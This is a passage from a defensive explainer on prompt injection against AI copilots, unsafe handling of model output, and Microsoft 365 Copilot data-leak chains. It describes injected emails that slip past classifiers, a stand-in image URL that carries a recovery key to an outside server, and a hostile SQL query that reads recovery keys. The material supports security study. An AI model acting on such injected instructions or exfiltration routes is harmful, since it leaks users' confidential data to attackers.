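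Attackers can learn from each failure, and a text that works once will often work again. When Dziemian and colleagues reran successful attacks on the same models, those against the Claude and GPT families worked again at least half the time. An attacker who subscribes to the same copilot could make the 200 attempts on a private account, where the victim can't see them, and send the company only the text that worked. David C recommends logging failed tool calls, because attackers usually have to refine an attack and the failures may give them away. That should catch someone who practises on the live system, but not someone who has practised elsewhere.

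### From a competition to a company

The competition's rates don't carry over directly to a company's copilot, because they overstate the risk in some ways and understate it in others. Unlike a stranger writing to the helpdesk, participants saw the whole conversation their text would enter, knew exactly which tool call they had to cause, and could watch the response before trying again. Dziemian and colleagues therefore treat their rates as an upper limit on what an attacker could do in a single turn, and warn against reading them as measures of security in real use.

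The rates also leave out many cases in which the agent did what the attacker wanted but revealed it in the reply, because an attack had to stay hidden to count. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action about 16% of the time, nearly double its headline rate, and even the more resistant models did so 1% to 3% of the time. Finding out afterwards doesn't help the user much if the agent has already sent a file outside the company. The competition also excluded attacks that unfold over several turns.

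The rate also depends on which attacks are used. Claude Opus 4.5 had a rate of 0.5% in the competition, where beginners' attempts counted as much as experts', but The Decoder reported a rate of 4.7% on the Gray Swan benchmark, which used only very strong attacks. Both numbers are valid, but a company that quotes one should know which kind of attacker it describes.

The biggest unknown is how many attacks will arrive. A success rate measures only how likely each attempt is to work. A small firm might receive no serious attempts in a year, whereas a bank might receive thousands, many of them copies of one message. If a thousand employees get the same email, the outcomes aren't independent, because the attack may fail or succeed on nearly all their copilots, depending on whether that text works on that product.

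### When a low rate is good enough

Optimists about models can fairly point out that companies accept imperfect controls all the time. Spam filters miss messages and employees fall for fraud, but firms still use email and hire people. On this view, the decision depends on the expected loss, which is the number of attempts times the average chance that each succeeds times the cost of a success. This calculation doesn't assume that attempts are independent, because clustering doesn't change the expected number of successes as long as the average rate is right.

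If 1,000 hostile emails a year reached the helpdesk copilot, about 38 would succeed at the 3.77% failure rate from OpenAI's internal tests, and about two at the 0.21% rate. If the worst result is a misfiled ticket that costs $50 to fix, the lower rate cuts the annual loss from about $1,900 to about $100. An elaborate new control would be hard to justify to save that last $100. But if each success exposes the payroll and costs $500,000, the expected loss at the lower rate is still about $1 million a year.

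The optimists are right, then, about many uses. A copilot that summarises wiki pages in plain text, with no links or tools, could reasonably rely on a resistant model and a classifier. This is compatible with David C's advice to make injection harder as well as limit what it can achieve. He objects to relying on the model when a single successful injection would be intolerable, because the chance of any success then matters more than the average success rate.

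Even for low-stakes uses, a team should expect the measured success rate to go out of date. The harm from a misfiled ticket is fairly stable, but the rate can change when the supplier replaces the model, the team connects a new tool, or attackers get access to a better model of their own.

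## What goes wrong when other software runs the output?

A copilot's output becomes dangerous when it reaches an interpreter, a program that carries out commands it finds in text. Until then, it is as harmless as text in a log file, even if an attacker chose every character. Web browsers, databases and command shells are all interpreters, and each has special characters that separate commands from data.

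Attackers were exploiting interpreters long before language models existed. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) examined eight classic web flaws and concluded that the model usually doesn't create the flaw, but gives attackers a new route to it. The established controls therefore still apply, and most of them are ordinary code that works even if the model is easily manipulated.

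| Interpreter | Classic flaw | How a copilot's output gets there | Control that fits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web browser | Cross-site scripting: text runs as a script | A page inserts the answer as HTML | Encode the text for the page, or allow only a few formatting tags |
| Database | SQL injection: text changes the query | The model supplies a value or writes the query | Parameterised queries for values; a restricted account and approved query forms for whole queries |
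| Shell | Command injection: text adds a command | A tool builds a command line from the model's arguments | Start a permitted program directly and pass its arguments separately |
| Code evaluator | Code injection: text runs as code | The model writes code, or software pastes the model's value into code | Avoid evaluating text; otherwise use isolated execution |
| File system | Path traversal: a file name leads outside the intended folder | The model chooses a name or location | Work out the full path, then check the folder |
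| Template engine | Template injection: text runs as part of a template | Software uses the answer as the template | Keep the template fixed and insert the answer as a value |
| Build pipeline | Hostile code runs with the pipeline's credentials | A coding copilot changes code or build scripts | Build in isolation, without credentials |
| Package installer | Malicious package | The model names a package, which it may have invented | Install only approved packages and verify their versions |

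A single cleaning step right after the model produces its output can't replace these controls, because each interpreter has different special characters. The apostrophe in O'Brien is harmless on a web page but can end a value early in a badly built database query. Deleting every apostrophe would misspell the name and still leave in the angle brackets that a browser interprets as HTML tags. Each sink therefore needs its own protection, applied just before it uses the output.

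### Browsers

If the helpdesk copilot's chat panel inserts answers into the page as raw HTML, a script in an answer will run in the employee's browser. The script can then read what the page can access and act as the employee. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a demonstration against DeepSeek's chat site in which the prompt contained an encoded script. The model decoded it, the page ran it, and the script could read the user's login token. A filter that searched the prompt for scripts could easily have missed this one, because it was readable only in the output.

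A script can also run later, in the browser of a more valuable victim. If the helpdesk copilot writes a summary containing the script into a ticket, the script might run the next day when an administrator opens the ticket.

The main control is encoding, which replaces special characters with codes that the browser displays as ordinary text. An opening angle bracket, for example, becomes `&lt;`. If the panel needs bold text and lists, a sanitiser can keep a few harmless tags and remove the rest. OWASP also recommends a content security policy, a set of rules the server sends to the browser about which scripts may run. Links and images can still carry data out of the company without any script, so they need separate controls.

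Software has to encode all model output before displaying it, whichever code path the output takes. Ma, Rong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities*, describe how an automated tool tried to repair such a flaw in ChuanhuChatGPT, an open-source chat interface. The tool's repair encoded HTML in ordinary messages but not in messages that other code had already wrapped, so one attack still worked. The developers' own fix sanitised the text of every message at the last step before display.

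### A worked example: the asset database

Suppose the helpdesk copilot's asset database has two tables. The `devices` table lists each device's kind, owner, model and warranty date. The `recovery_keys` table holds the codes that unlock the laptops' encrypted disks. An employee asks when their laptop's warranty ends.

In the safer design, a developer has written the query in advance:

```sql
SELECT model, warranty_end
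FROM devices
WHERE owner_id = ? AND kind = ?
```

The question marks are placeholders. The application fills the first with the employee's number, which it takes from their login, and the model fills the second with "laptop". If a hostile email makes the model supply SQL instead, the database searches for a kind of device with that name and finds none.

The query's safety also depends on which part of the system fills each gap. If the model supplied the owner's number, the email could make it supply a colleague's instead, and the query would return the colleague's laptop. Parameterisation wouldn't prevent this, because the colleague's number is a valid value.

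Now suppose that staff want to ask broader questions, such as which laptop model breaks most often, so the team lets the model write the whole query. After reading a hostile email, the model might write:

```sql
SELECT * FROM recovery_keys
```

The application can still send a query written by the model as a prepared statement, the usual way of running a parameterised query. But the statement has no placeholders for values to protect, and the database runs the command as the model wrote it. OWASP recommends parameterised queries or prepared statements for all database operations that involve model output. That is good advice for values, but it could give a team false confidence when the model writes the whole query. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian state that prepared statements aren't enough when the model generates the query's structure.

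Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite earlier work by Pedro and colleagues, known as P2SQL, that demonstrated the problem in a chatbot whose database account could read every table and run any kind of statement. An outsider could get the contents of the users table by asking for them in plain English. In an indirect version, the attacker planted a record in the database that made the chatbot tell later users there were no job postings. Attackers could also bypass instructions in the prompt not to delete or change data. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian couldn't reproduce similar attacks on the newer models they tested in April 2026, although they didn't try to optimise the attacks.

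Teams can instead restrict what any query is able to do. In the table below, each row adds a protection to those above it.

| Protection | Query that deletes device records | Query that reads recovery keys | Query that reads a colleague's device record |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prepared statement only | Runs | Runs | Runs |
| Read-only account | Blocked | Runs | Runs |
| Access to the `devices` table only | Blocked | Blocked | Runs |
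| Row-level permissions | Blocked | Blocked | Returns nothing |

Row-level permissions are database rules that limit which rows a query can return, in this case to the signed-in employee's devices. The application has to give the database the employee's identity in a way the query can't alter. Some systems keep the identity in a session setting that queries can change, so a hostile query could change it before reading anything.

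These permissions also block the question about which laptop breaks most often, since answering it requires other people's records. Developers can handle such questions by writing a small set of approved query forms, such as "count faults by model", and letting the model choose one and fill in the values. The query's structure is then fixed again, so parameterisation works. Staff can ask only what somebody thought of in advance, but that seems acceptable for a helpdesk. A data analyst's copilot might need free-form queries, and it would then be safer to give it a copy of the data without the sensitive columns.

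Limits on query results reduce the damage from any harmful query that gets through. If the company has 4,000 devices and each query returns at most 20 rows, copying the whole table takes at least 200 queries, which gives monitoring a reasonable chance of detecting it. The limit should cover the size of the result as well as the number of rows, because a query can combine thousands of values into one very long row. A time limit also helps, since even a read-only query can slow the database for everyone else.

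Searching the query for dangerous words is a poor substitute for these protections. Ma and colleagues describe a flaw in LlamaIndex, a framework for connecting models to data, that let model-written SQL attach a new database and so create files on the server. An automated repair banned the dangerous keywords but also rejected harmless queries that used a name like "attach". The developers' fix used a feature of the database, SQLite, that blocks the action however the query is worded.

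### Shells and generated code

A shell treats certain characters as the end of one command and the start of another. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a flaw that the security company Snyk found in an MCP server for running Amazon cloud commands. The server ran any text after such a character as a second command. Servers like this often run on a developer's own computer, where outsiders can't connect to them, but an attacker could still exploit the flaw by planting an instruction in a code file. When the developer asked the assistant to list some cloud storage, the model would add the attacker's command to the tool call.

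The server could have prevented this by starting the Amazon program directly and passing each argument separately, so that no shell read the line. Many agents instead search commands for dangerous text. SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026) reports that researchers at Adversa AI got past such filters in 10 of the 11 agents they examined, because the shell rewrites a command after the filter has checked it.

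A tool should also have a fixed list of the programs it may start. Microsoft (2026) found no such list in a development version of AutoGen Studio, its prototyping tool for AI agents. AutoGen Studio accepted connections from the computer it ran on, didn't require a login on the relevant channel, and started whatever program the request named. An outsider couldn't connect directly, but if an agent on the same computer opened the outsider's web page, a script in the page could make the connection without the model writing a command. The developers fixed the flaw before the affected code reached a published package.

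Some copilots have to run code that the model writes, for instance to analyse a spreadsheet. Encoding can't help because the output is supposed to be a program. The team can run the code in a sandbox that has no credentials, no network access and only the files the task needs, and delete the sandbox afterwards. The code may still be hostile, but there is little for it to steal or damage. Its output remains untrusted.

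### Files and templates

A sandbox is secure only if the functions that move data out of it are secure too. In May, Microsoft (2026) described a flaw in Semantic Kernel, its open-source framework for building AI agents. Agents could run code in an isolated cloud sandbox, and a helper function copied files from there to the host, the computer running the agent. A developer had accidentally marked this function as a tool for the model, so the model could choose where on the host to save each file.

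An attacker could therefore use injected instructions to make the model write a script in the sandbox and then copy it into the host's Windows Startup folder, where it would run the next time someone signed in. The attack did not have to break the sandbox's isolation, because the copying function moved the model's output to the host.

Microsoft removed the function from the model's list of tools, which was enough to break the attack. For developers who call the function from their own code, it added a check that works out the full path and then compares it with a list of permitted folders. The check has to work out the full path first because a path can begin in a permitted folder and then step back out of it. Where practical, it is simpler for the application to choose the file name. For example, the helpdesk copilot could save each attachment under its ticket number.

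Template engines produce standard documents by filling in blanks, and many can also evaluate expressions inside a template. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite an application, documented by Fengyu Liu and colleagues in 2025, that used the model's answer as a template in the Jinja2 engine. An expression in the answer could then run commands on the server. Keeping the template in the application's code and inserting the answer as a value prevents this, because the engine prints the value without evaluating it. If the document is a web page or an HTML email, the application still needs to encode the value for HTML.

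### Build pipelines and invented packages

Changes proposed by a coding copilot often go to a build pipeline, an automated system that compiles, tests and releases software. Many pipelines test a change before anyone has reviewed it, and some hold credentials for publishing the finished product. A malicious line in a test script could then run with those credentials. Teams can avoid this by testing proposed changes in an isolated environment without credentials, and by preventing the copilot from editing the pipeline's configuration.

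Builds also depend on package installers, which download other people's code by name. OWASP warns that models sometimes suggest packages that don't exist, and that developers may download malware as a result. An attacker who learns which names a model tends to invent can publish a malicious package under one of them and wait for someone to install it. This needs no prompt injection, because the model makes the mistake by itself.

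Checking that a package exists does not protect a company once an attacker has published it. The company can instead run its own registry of approved packages and have a person review any new name. It should also install packages in isolation, because many run code during installation.

Approving a package name isn't enough if the code behind it can change, so developers also pin packages to a reviewed version. Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026) describes how this control failed in Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI. None of the four verified that the plugin code they fetched matched the pinned version, so an attacker who controlled the plugin's repository could substitute other code. The flaw was in the agents' installation code, not in the model's output, but it undermined a control that teams might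 use to contain that output. As of mid-September 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI had fixed the flaw, Microsoft hadn't, and Google had retired Gemini CLI without a fix.

### Why a valid value can still be hostile

Developers often check tool calls against a schema, which defines the fields a call must contain and the form each value must take. This check catches many accidents and some attacks, but a hostile value in the right form will pass it.

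Microsoft demonstrated this with a second flaw in Semantic Kernel, using a test agent that searched for hotels. The search tool accepted any text as the city. The framework pasted that text into a line of Python code and ran the line to filter the hotels, so a carefully written "city" could run as code. A single prompt was enough to start another program on the host.

The framework's developers had anticipated this danger and added a validator, which checked that the line had the expected structure and contained no names from a list of dangerous ones before running it. The researchers' line passed because it had the right structure and used dangerous names that weren't on the list. Microsoft's vulnerability record rates the flaw 9.9 out of 10 for severity and lists it as not exploited. The fix relies mainly on lists of what the line may contain, including operations and functions. For a simple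 search by city, comparing the text directly without building a line of code from it would be safer still.

A stricter schema allows fewer outputs but may still allow the wrong ones. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a shop's chatbot that looked up orders by a number made up of fixed letters and six digits. A check on that pattern would accept a million numbers. The chatbot gave out other customers' email and delivery addresses because nothing checked whether the order belonged to the person asking.

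The helpdesk copilot's password reset has the same weakness. Suppose the tool takes an employee number, such as E10482. Software can check that the number is an E followed by five digits, that it belongs to a current employee, and that the signed-in user may reset that account. But if a hostile email asks for a reset of the user's own account, the number passes all three checks, and nothing in it shows whether the user wanted the reset.

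A list of permitted values is dependable only if it is enforced in code. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a concert-ticket assistant, TicketOracle, that could fetch web addresses, and tested seven models with it. In one version, the system prompt listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others. The attacker planted a concert review claiming that the list now included an internal address. Llama 3.3 70B fetched the address and disclosed the data in all ten trials, but in only six of ten when the prompt contained no list.

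The other six models resisted every time in the version with the list. Ten trials in a single conversation are too few to show that the list made Llama worse, but they show that the list did not protect Llama. If the application itself had checked each address against the list, the review would have had no effect.

### How common are these flaws?

Researchers have counted published vulnerabilities of this kind in open-source AI software. LLMSmith, an early project by Tong Liu and colleagues in 2024, combined automated code analysis with test prompts to trace paths from user input, through a model, to functions that execute code. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian report that it found 20 vulnerabilities in 11 frameworks.

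In *Demystifying LLM Supply Chain Vulnerabilities in the Wild*, Wang, Zhao and colleagues (2025) collected 529 vulnerabilities from 77 software repositories and classified their causes by hand. Of these, 431 were traditional flaws that could occur in any software. Only 24 (4.5%) came from failing to validate what a model had generated.

Ma and colleagues used a stricter test, asking whether an attack could work without the model. They began with 2,888 vulnerabilities in 230 open-source components, and five security researchers reviewed them manually. The resulting dataset, LiLCVE, contains 116 vulnerabilities in systems that use language models, but only 41 of them require the model to take part in the attack. The two studies classify these flaws a little differently:

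| What the output did | Wang and colleagues | Ma and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Ran as code or a command | 11 | 20 |
| Ran as, or altered, a database query | 5 | 7 |
| Manipulated files | 4 | No separate category |
| Ran or displayed unsafely in a page | 3 | 4 |
| Made a server send a request | 1 | No separate category |
| Chose a tool or its arguments | No separate category | 7 |
| Misled software that parses output | No separate category | 3 |
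| Total | 24 | 41 |

Code and command execution make up nearly half of the total in both studies, so it seems sensible for a team to start by removing unnecessary ways to run code. The studies draw on overlapping public databases and probably include some of the same vulnerabilities, so their agreement is weaker evidence than agreement between independent studies would be.

Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild*, studied 295 GitHub security advisories (public notices about flaws in software packages) that dated from January 2025 to January 2026 and mentioned components related to language models. They took a random sample of 100 from the advisories about packages that implement or commonly support such models, and labelled it using OWASP's 2025 categories. Twelve involved improper output handling, and ten of those also involved prompt injection.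 The underlying coding mistakes were all familiar types, which suggests that existing tools for finding injection flaws are still useful.

The distinction Ma and colleagues draw is also useful for reading news reports. Callahan, in *Agent Frameworks Fail Security Boundary Test*, reports that in August 2026 Check Point disclosed 11 vulnerabilities, including path traversal, in six major agent frameworks. A flaw in an agent framework isn't necessarily an output-handling flaw, since an attacker may be able to exploit it without involving a model.

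All these studies count published flaws in open-source software. They can't show how often attackers exploit such flaws, or how many exist in closed products such as Microsoft 365 Copilot. The small percentages aren't very reassuring either, because the flaws tend to be serious. Ma and colleagues found that 21 of their 41 were rated "critical".

These flaws are also hard to repair automatically. Ma and colleagues tested 20 combinations of repair tools and models. On average, a combination fixed 25.8% of the 41 flaws, and the best fixed 22 (54%). The newest models tested are now some way behind the best available. A repair counted only if it blocked every test attack and left the software's normal functions working. Many failed repairs did only one of these.

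## How can an answer on the screen leak data?

A copilot's answer can leak confidential data even if nothing in it runs as code. When a browser displays a page with an image, it requests the image from the address the page gives. That address can contain text, and the server that receives the request normally logs the whole address.

Suppose an employee asks the helpdesk copilot for the recovery key to a locked laptop while a hostile email is also in the context. The copilot answers correctly, but the injected instructions make it add an image with an address like this:

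`pictures.example/logo.png?note=KEY`

In a real attack, the laptop's recovery key would replace the word KEY. When the browser requests the image, the key ends up in the server's log. The server doesn't have to return an image, so the employee sees the right answer and perhaps a broken-image icon.

Any component that fetches the address, such as a browser, a link previewer or a file scanner, sends the text to whoever owns the server. Microsoft notes that the data can go in the path, the parameters or a subdomain (the part in front of the main domain name). With a subdomain, just looking up the address can leak the data, because the lookup may reach a name server that the attacker runs. An ordinary link can also carry data, but somebody has to click it.

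The technique was well known before anyone used it against Microsoft's Copilot. Willison (2025), a software developer who writes about AI security, had seen versions of it in a dozen products by the time EchoLeak became public.

### Content security policy

The usual browser control is a content security policy, a set of rules that a web server sends with a page. It can list the domains from which the page may load images. If the helpdesk copilot's page may load images only from the company's own domain, the browser won't send the request to pictures.example, so the key doesn't leak. This control is deterministic, meaning that ordinary code enforces it and the result doesn't depend on the model's judgement.

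But the policy covers only what a browser loads for that page. It doesn't apply to requests that a server makes or stop a person from following a link. The browser checks where a request is going but not whether the address contains a secret, and it can't determine what the receiving server will do with that address.

Large products also tend to need long lists. The list that Microsoft 365 Copilot used for images in 2025 had 29 different entries, 11 of which were wildcards covering every subdomain of a domain.

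### Three disclosures in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Between June 2025 and December 2026, researchers published three sets of attacks that made Microsoft 365 Copilot leak data through its output. Each was a chain of flaws that together got the data past several controls.

Aim Labs, the research team at Aim Security, found EchoLeak. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes an email that got past Microsoft's input classifier because its instructions seemed to be written for the human recipient and never mentioned AI. The email also had sections on several common staff questions, such as leave of absence, which made Copilot more likely to retrieve it. Once the email was in its context, Copilot looked for the most sensitive information there and put it into the address of an image. The email also gave a compliance reason for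 not citing it, so the answer didn't name its source.

The SearchLeak attack started with a link to a genuine Microsoft page. According to Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), the part of the link meant for search terms reached the model as instructions. One click made Copilot search the victim's mailbox and put an email's subject line into an image address. Many services put login codes in the subject line, and a code may still work when the attacker reads it.

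In *ReLeak*, the most recent disclosure, Simonovich (2026) described three zero-click attack chains on behalf of Cato AI Labs on 3 December 2026. Cato AI Labs is the team that found EchoLeak, and was renamed after Cato Networks bought Aim Security. The researchers used AI agents to write and test the malicious prompts, according to Infosecurity Magazine. All three chains began with an email that got past the classifier, but they differed in how the data left.

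| Chain | Entry point | Controls relied on | What sent the data out | User action needed | Severity score out of 10 | Reported to Microsoft | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Email | Input classifier, link filter, content security policy | A Microsoft Teams service | An ordinary question to Copilot | Microsoft 9.3; US database 7.5 | January 2025 | May 2025 |
| SearchLeak | Link to a Microsoft page | Cleaning of the finished answer, content security policy | Bing's image search | One click | Microsoft 6.5; US database 7.5 or 6.5 (accounts differ) | No date given | By 15 June 2026 |
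| ReLeak, images | Email | Input classifier, content security policy | Bing | An ordinary request to Copilot | Not yet published | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 15 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, documents | Email | Input classifier | Microsoft's background file services | An ordinary request to Copilot | Not yet published | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 11 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, code interpreter | Email | Input classifier, the sandbox's network block | Code running in the sandbox | An ordinary request to Copilot | Microsoft 8.6 | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September 2026 |

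EchoLeak's dates come from Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, and the period in which the researchers reported ReLeak comes from Punto Informatico's *ReLeak*.

The scores use a common scale, but they depend on judgements about what to count. The EchoLeak record at GCVE (2025), a public vulnerability database, shows that Microsoft's score was higher than the US National Vulnerability Database's because only Microsoft counted harm beyond the flawed component and a slight risk of data being altered.

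Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* scores SearchLeak 6.5, normally a medium rating, but labels it "Critical". Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* reports that the US database gave it 7.5, on the assumption that the victim didn't have to do anything. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* disputes the 7.5 and says that both records showed 6.5. A team that ranked flaws by Microsoft's scores alone would put SearchLeak well below EchoLeak, even though SearchLeak could reach any email or indexed file the victim could open.

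Microsoft has patched all of these flaws on its own servers, and nobody has reported a real attack that used them. Microsoft told the EchoLeak researchers that no customers were affected, and its SearchLeak record lists the flaw as not exploited. For ReLeak, the only evidence is that Cato knew of no victims. A company would have trouble finding out for itself whether it had been attacked, because the stolen data would have gone out in requests sent to or by Microsoft's services.

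### Cleaning that missed the link or came too late

Before EchoLeak, Microsoft already filtered Copilot's answers to remove links and images that pointed outside the company. Copilot formats its answers in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and so on. A writer can put a link's address directly after its text, or put a label there and give the address elsewhere. The filter recognised only the first form, but the chat panel displayed both, and the attack used the second.

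A filter and a display program can read the same text differently when each interprets it separately. Adding a missing notation to the filter fixes only that case, because Markdown has many variants and programs handle them differently. A builder can avoid the problem by having the software interpret the answer only once. The software turns the answer into a structured list of paragraphs, links and images, checks every address in that list, and builds the display from the same list, so an unchecked address can't appear on the screen.

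In SearchLeak, the cleaning worked but came too late. Microsoft wrapped Copilot's finished answer in markers that make a browser show HTML tags as plain text. But Copilot streams its answers, displaying each piece of text as the model produces it, so the browser treated the tags as real HTML until the answer was complete. It requested the image as soon as the tag appeared, before the markers were added.

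Programmers call this a race condition, because the outcome depends on which of two events happens first. The flaw is easy to miss in testing, because the finished page showed harmless text where the image had been, and a tester might have concluded that the control worked.

### When a permitted service fetches for others

Both attacks needed a service on a permitted domain to forward the browser's request to the attacker's server, because the content security policy would have blocked a direct request.

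The EchoLeak researchers first tried SharePoint. The policy permitted every SharePoint site, including any that an attacker set up as a paying customer. This wasn't enough by itself, because site owners can no longer run their own code on SharePoint's servers. But SharePoint could fetch content from outside addresses to embed in a page, and the researchers used this function to send the data out. It worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

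They then found a Teams service that fetched outside addresses without an invitation. The browser sent its request to Teams, which the policy allowed. Teams then requested the attacker's address, with the confidential text still in it. The browser's policy didn't apply to that second request because a Microsoft server made it.

Server-side request forgery means getting a server to make a request of the attacker's choice, and it is much older than language models. SearchLeak used this technique with Bing's search for similar pictures, which has to fetch the original picture from the address it receives. Bing's domain was on the list of permitted domains that Ravia had published a year earlier. ReLeak's image route also went through Bing, and the researchers reported it to Microsoft less than ten weeks after the SearchLeak disclosure. Whatever Microsoft changed in June evidently didn't stop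 every request of this kind.

A list of permitted domains seems to fail when a permitted service will fetch addresses for others. In EchoLeak, SearchLeak and the first ReLeak route, the browser obeyed the policy and the data still reached the attacker. Varonis therefore advises teams to review the list and treat any domain that fetches user-supplied addresses as a possible route for leaking data.

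A permitted domain can also be unsafe because of who controls it. In ForcedLeak, the attack on Salesforce's agents, a permitted domain had expired, so anyone could have registered it. A team therefore needs to know who controls each domain on the list, as well as what the services there will do with a request.

Such lists are still useful. The policy blocked the simple version of all three image attacks and forced the researchers to look for a permitted service that would pass the data on. If the list had contained only a server that returns fixed pictures, they would have found no such service. Microsoft's list was weak because it was long and permitted whole domains, each with many functions. Bing's domain may well have been included so that ordinary pictures would load, but including it also permitted every other function at that domain that answers an image request.

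### Requests that don't come from the browser

The other two ReLeak routes don't fit the lesson about permitted domains, since neither depended on the browser loading anything.

In the document route, Copilot created a file with a link containing confidential data. It saved the file to OneDrive or SharePoint, where Microsoft's background services processed it and fetched the link. The researchers made this work with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. Nobody had to open the file, and the leak could happen after the chat had ended. Cleaning the answer in the chat panel wouldn't have prevented the leak, because the link was in the file.

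The third route used Copilot's code interpreter, which runs Python that the model writes. According to Microsoft's documentation, the interpreter's sandbox blocked outgoing network traffic, but the researchers found ways around the block and sent data directly to an outside server. Copilot Cowork's sandbox had failed in a similar way that summer, so a team should test whether its own block works.

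The broader lesson from all five chains is that every component that handles the output and can make network requests needs its own limit. A content security policy limits one of those components.

### Microsoft's case for blocking the exits

Microsoft distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to work, from deterministic ones, which can guarantee that a particular attack fails. It prefers deterministic defences where they are possible. It says nobody yet knows how to detect prompt injection deterministically, so it assumes that some injections will succeed and tries to design its products to block the harm they could do.

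Microsoft compares blocking these leaks to the way operating systems handle memory errors. Programmers can't find every error, so operating systems make the ones that remain hard to exploit. When the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported that Copilot could leak data through Markdown images, Microsoft blocked the leak instead of relying on the model to refuse. It says it then looked for variants and blocked other routes, including certain untrusted links.

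This is a good argument because a product has a limited number of ways to send data out, and engineers can in principle list and close them, whereas attackers can always reword an instruction.

ReLeak shows that a guarantee covers only what the engineers specified. Throughout the attacks, the browser loaded images only from the permitted domains. But Microsoft's customers needed a much stronger guarantee, that no text from the context would reach an outsider's server, and no single control enforced it.

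Blocking known routes is also limited because new features can add more routes. If a copilot can only answer questions, the chat panel is the only route to consider. If it can also create documents, data could leak through any service that processes them, and a code interpreter adds another route. If the company adds features faster than its engineers can examine where the output goes, there will always be routes they haven't blocked.

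Cato's researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato has an interest in saying so because it sells AI security products, and the verdict is somewhat harsh. The researchers had to find new flaws to get the data out, and Microsoft fixed the interpreter flaw within about seven weeks of the report. But the other two fixes took between 12 and 16 weeks, and the reappearance of Bing so soon after SearchLeak is hard to defend.

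The failures suggest reversing the default rather than returning to detection, so that output can't cause any outside request until somebody has examined and permitted the route. If somebody then overlooks a service, the result is a missing picture or a broken preview, which users will report, instead of a leak that nobody sees.

### What a customer can change

A company that buys Microsoft 365 Copilot can't rewrite the product's content security policy or the filter on its answers. Ravia knew of no administrator setting or user behaviour that would have prevented EchoLeak. Customers can still limit the data an attack could reach.

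Copilot can read whatever the signed-in user can read, so removing access that people no longer need reduces what a leak could expose. Microsoft's Purview tools can stop Copilot from summarising files with particular sensitivity labels. These measures help more with documents than with mail, because a login code in an inbox won't have a label and the inbox's owner needs access to it.

Reddy and Gujral say that Microsoft's patches reportedly added options to restrict Copilot's use of messages from outside the company. This restriction would remove the easiest entry point, but a salesperson whose copilot can't read customers' emails may have little use for it. The restriction might suit teams that handle sensitive material and correspond mostly with colleagues. Where a product lets administrators turn off file creation or the code interpreter, it makes sense to do so for staff who don't use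 them.

Monitoring can catch some attacks. Varonis recommends looking for Copilot search links that contain HTML tags or instructions to put data into an image address. According to The Next Web, Varonis also recommends watching for unusual requests to Bing's image functions. Both checks depend on traffic that the company can see. In the ReLeak document route, Microsoft's servers sent the data out, so the company's own network logs would have shown nothing unusual.

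Varonis also advises users to inspect links before clicking. This is a reasonable habit, but SearchLeak's link led to a real Microsoft page, and ReLeak didn't involve a click.

### What a builder can change

A team that builds its own copilot has more control, and the simplest step is to stop automatic fetching. The helpdesk copilot's chat panel doesn't need images from outside servers, so it can show only those the application supplies. The content security policy should then allow images only from the application's own server. If the copilot also posts its answers to a messaging app, the team should turn off link previews there, because the app may fetch every address in a message.

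Links are harder to give up, since an answer about the VPN is more useful with a link to the wiki page. But the model doesn't have to write the address. The application can number the documents it retrieves and have the model cite those numbers. If the model produces "document 3", the application looks up the address in its own records and creates the link. The model can cite the wrong document, but it can't add a recovery key to the address. If the number doesn't match a retrieved document, the application shows no link.

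The application could extend this to outside links by allowing an address only if it appeared, character for character, in a retrieved document. An address that the supplier wrote last week can't contain a key that the copilot looked up today. However, if an attacker owns *n* addresses and can see which one somebody opens, the choice of address still reveals up to log₂ *n* bits of information per visit.

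A six-digit login code contains about 20 bits. With eight addresses, each visit reveals three bits, so the attacker would need seven visits to learn the code. Seven clicks is a lot to expect from a person. But if the email supplied 64 addresses and the software fetched links automatically, four fetches would be enough. Exact matching therefore works well for links that people click but poorly for anything the software fetches by itself. Limiting each answer to one or two outside links also helps.

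Streaming can be safe if the software cleans each piece of text before the browser receives it. However, a link or tag may arrive in several pieces, none of which looks dangerous alone. The software can display ordinary words immediately but hold back anything that might be the start of a link, image or tag until it can check the whole item. The delay is usually too short to notice. A simpler option is to insert the streamed text as plain text, which the browser never interprets as HTML, and add formatting and checked links at the end. Waiting for the complete answer also works, but users may dislike the delay.

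Generated files need similar treatment. Before saving a document, the software can remove references to outside images and templates and rebuild links as described above. This reduces the risk, but file formats are complicated and some references may remain. Every service that later opens the file should therefore have its own limits on outbound connections, including programs that make thumbnails, convert documents to PDF, index them for search or scan them for viruses. Most of these can work without internet access. A scanner that has to check links can look up the domain in a list of known malicious sites without requesting the full address.

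The limits should cover DNS lookups as well as web requests, because data can leave in a subdomain. They should also cover the company's own fetching services. For example, if the helpdesk has a tool that retrieves web pages, the code sandbox and the document converter shouldn't be able to call it, because its requests could carry data out of the company, as Bing's could at Microsoft.

A team can test these routes without a real attack. It sets up its own server, creates a unique address on it for each route, and puts those addresses into chat answers, tickets and every type of file the copilot can produce. No request should reach the server unless the team has deliberately permitted that route. The test should run for several days, since background services may not process a file until long after the chat has ended. The team should repeat it whenever the copilot gains a new output format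 or another service starts to read its files.

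## Can internal systems still trust a request that comes from a copilot?

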